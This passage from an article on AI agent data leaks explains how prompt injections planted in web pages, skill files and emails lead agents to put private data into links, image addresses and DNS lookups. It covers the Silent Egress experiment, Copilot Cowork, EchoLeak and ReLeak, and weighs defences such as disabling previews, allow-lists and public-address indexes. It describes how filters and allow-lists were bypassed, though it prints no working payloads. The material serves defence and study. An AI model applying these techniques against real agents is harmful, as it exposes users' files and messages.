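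One logged request is enough to show that a pairing can leak. The reports can't show how common the problem is, because the testers were self-selected and chose what to test. A pairing might collect many reports because many people use it, and another might look safe only because the tester had already turned previews off. The site also tests only the final step, the preview request, and doesn't measure how easily an attacker could get the agent to write the link. The OpenClaw finding is firmer than the rest because PromptArmor traced the leak to a particular setting and found that changing it stopped the leak.

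### Previews that carry instructions in

The *Silent Egress* experiment, also from February 2026, examined previews as a way to get malicious instructions into an agent rather than data out of it. Lan and colleagues ran their agent on qwen2.5:7b, a model small enough for a personal computer. They planted the instructions in a page's title, description, body or link text, and sometimes sent the agent through redirects first.

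The agent sent data to the researchers' server in 423 of 480 runs, or 88 percent. The paper's abstract gives the rate as about 0.89. The agent sent nothing in 120 runs with harmless pages, so the planted instructions were the cause. In 95 percent of the successful attacks, the visible answer gave no sign of the theft.

In the experiment, the preview came before the model's answer and only delivered the instructions to the model, whereas Slack fetches a link after the model has written it. Switching off Slack's previews would therefore not have protected the agent.

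The 88 percent figure is a poor guide to commercial products. The researchers put the secret directly in the model's input and gave the model almost no safety instructions. They argued that larger models could be more vulnerable because they follow instructions better, but they didn't test any. Claude Opus 4.6 resisted every email in the public challenge, which is evidence against that argument.

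### File links in Teams messages

A newer Claude model did much worse in a May 2026 test of Copilot Cowork, a Microsoft agent that can read a user's work files and send email and Teams messages on their behalf. PromptArmor's *Microsoft Copilot Cowork Exfiltrates Files* describes an attack that begins when a user uploads a "skill" they found online, which is a file of instructions for a recurring task. PromptArmor added five malicious lines to an 81-line skill.

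When the user asked for a review of the week's work, Cowork collected download links for recent files. Anyone who has these links can download the files without a password. Cowork put the links into the addresses of images in a Teams message to the user. When the user opened the message, Teams loaded the images, which sent the links to the attacker's server.

Microsoft said in its documentation that Cowork would ask permission before posting in Teams. PromptArmor found that it didn't ask when the recipient was the user, and that users couldn't change this. These messages could still trigger requests to an outside server, though the exemption probably seemed harmless because only the user would receive them.

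The attack worked in all five trials. It also worked when PromptArmor selected Claude Opus 4.7, so using a strong model was not enough to prevent it. That model found and leaked more files than Cowork's automatic mode did. Five trials is a small sample, though, and the malicious text was in a file of instructions that the agent was supposed to follow, which is harder to defend against than malicious text in strangers' emails.

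PromptArmor presented the attack as a risk in Cowork's design, and its account includes no response from Microsoft. PromptArmor had reported a different flaw in Cowork to Microsoft. Administrators can block downloads of sensitive files, but employees can then view those files only in a browser, not in Word or Excel.

### Who can turn previews off

Slack now warns developers about the preview leak in its security guide. The guide describes an attack much like Rehberger's, in which a malicious message contains instructions for a model to encode the last five messages in a channel and add them to a link. Slack recommends turning off link previews by default for any message that may contain a link written by a model. In its general guide to previews, it only asks developers to "consider" doing so.

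This is good advice, but Slack still leaves link previews on by default, so a developer who never reads the warning will probably build a bot that leaks data.

Slack also suggests adding rules to the model's standing instructions, such as a ban on putting private data in links, but admits this is "not a complete solution". Lan and colleagues tested a similar measure 30 times. Their small model still leaked data in two thirds of the runs when given a stern instruction to treat web content as data and never as commands. Marking outside text with special tags made no difference on its own, but combining the tags with the instruction lowered the leak rate to 57 percent.

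OpenClaw users can protect themselves on Telegram by adding `linkPreview: false` to the settings file. This is easy for a programmer, but many users will never open the file, so a safer default would help them more.

PromptArmor wants chat companies to consider preview controls for individual chats or channels. Administrators could then turn previews off wherever bots post. This would cover bots whose developers missed Slack's settings, and bots' answers that employees copy into their own messages there. PromptArmor thinks agent developers share the responsibility because they have to use the controls chat companies provide.

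### Allow-lists and EchoLeak

Companies that want to keep previews for useful links could use an allow-list, a list of approved sites, and block all others. Rehberger suggested one as a possible improvement to Anthropic's connector, and Slack recommends checking links from a model against one.

In Lan and colleagues' experiment, an allow-list stopped every attempt to send data out, but the test was easy because the attacker's site was obviously not on the list. They checked the agent's own web requests, whereas Slack's servers make the preview request, so the developer of a Slack bot has to check the link before posting the message.

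A harder problem is that an approved site may pass data on to an unapproved one. This happened in EchoLeak, a flaw in Microsoft 365 Copilot that the research team Aim Labs found in January 2025. In *Breaking down 'EchoLeak', the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability Enabling Data Exfiltration*, Ravia (2025) explains that the attacker only had to email the victim. The email's instructions were worded as if for a human employee, which got them past Microsoft's prompt injection filter. When the victim later asked Copilot about a related subject, it retrieved the email and followed the instructions.

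Copilot then wrote an image address containing private data. Microsoft allowed the browser to load images only from listed sites, and the attacker's server wasn't among them. But the list included a Teams service that would fetch content from another address on request. The browser contacted that service, which sent the data on to the attacker's server. The Teams service did much the same job as a server that fetches link previews.

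Aim Labs called EchoLeak the first zero-click AI vulnerability. That claim depends on a narrow definition, because Rehberger had been reporting since 2023 that images could leak data without a click. Ravia argues that EchoLeak differs because earlier attacks required the user to point the chatbot at a malicious document, or limited what the attacker could steal.

Microsoft needed several attempts to fix the flaw. Goldman (2025) reported in *New Microsoft Copilot flaw signals broader risk of AI agents being hacked* that Microsoft tried a fix in April and found further problems in May. Aim's co-founder Adir Gruss considered the five-month wait very long and attributed it partly to the flaw being new. According to *EchoLeak* (2025), a case study of the attack, Microsoft completed the fix in May, and the advisory for CVE-2025-32711 appeared on 11 June. Microsoft said no customers were affected.

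Researchers have since found other ways to get data out of Copilot through Microsoft's own services. *SearchLeak* (Taler, 2026) described an attack that could steal emails and login codes after one click. *Attackers tricked Copilot into leaking sensitive data through Bing* (Okemwa, 2026) identified Bing as the route.

On 3 December 2026, Simonovich disclosed three more attacks on Copilot, all zero-click, in *ReLeak* (2026). Each starts with an email that the victim does not have to open. In one, Copilot puts the data in an image address and the browser sends it to the attacker through Bing (Nexo Causal, *ReLeak*, 2026). The other two use a link in a saved file and code that Copilot runs (AIAIAI.FYI, *Cato AI Labs details three ReLeak zero-click attacks on Microsoft 365 Copilot*, 2026). Microsoft patched all three between 17 September and 15 November, and the researchers knew of no real-world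 attacks using them.

An allow-list is therefore only as safe as the least secure service on it. A short list of a company's own pages may work well for a Slack bot, but allowing all of a large technology company's domains is much riskier, because some service there may redirect visitors or fetch other pages for them.

### Checking the whole address

OpenAI chose to have its agents check whether a link's exact address is already public instead of relying on a list of trusted sites. *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (OpenAI, 2026) explains that trusted sites often redirect visitors elsewhere, and that strict lists produce so many warnings that people learn to click through them.

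OpenAI keeps an index of web addresses, built by a program that crawls the public web and has no access to users' conversations. The agent can automatically open any address in the index. For other addresses, the system either prompts the agent to try another site or shows the user a warning that the link may contain information from the conversation.

The rule would catch the fictional alarm code from the supplier's price list. An address ending in `d=heron-4417` would not be in the index unless someone had already published it, so the agent would ask before opening it. The agent would usually open an ordinary news article without asking.

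OpenAI promises only to stop agents from quietly leaking data through the address itself. A page that passes the check may still contain false information or malicious instructions, and a user may approve a bad link despite the warning. The rule covers only requests by OpenAI's agents, so it wouldn't stop Slack from previewing a link that an OpenAI model had written for someone else's bot. Slack could apply a similar rule to links in messages from apps. This would preserve most useful previews, but Slack would need its own index.

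Small exceptions can undermine this kind of rule. Anthropic's web-fetching tool could open only addresses that the user had typed, that its search tool had returned, or that were linked on pages it had already fetched. Willison (2026) described how a researcher exploited the exception for linked pages with a website full of generated links. The agent leaked private data through the sequence of links it followed, without writing an address itself.

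Data can also leave before a program requests any page. To find a website, a program first looks up its name in the Domain Name System (DNS), the internet's directory of site names. The lookup can reach a server that the site's owner controls, carrying any secret placed in the name. Lan and colleagues left this route out of their experiment. Poireault (2026), in *Vulnerabilities in Salesforce Agentforce Expose Wider AI Agent Risk*, reported that researchers had used DNS lookups to extract customer records from Agentforce, the AI agents made by Slack's owner, Salesforce. Fifteen months earlier, Gruss had named Agentforce as a product that might have flaws like EchoLeak. A defence that inspects an address only when the agent requests the page may act too late to stop such a leak.
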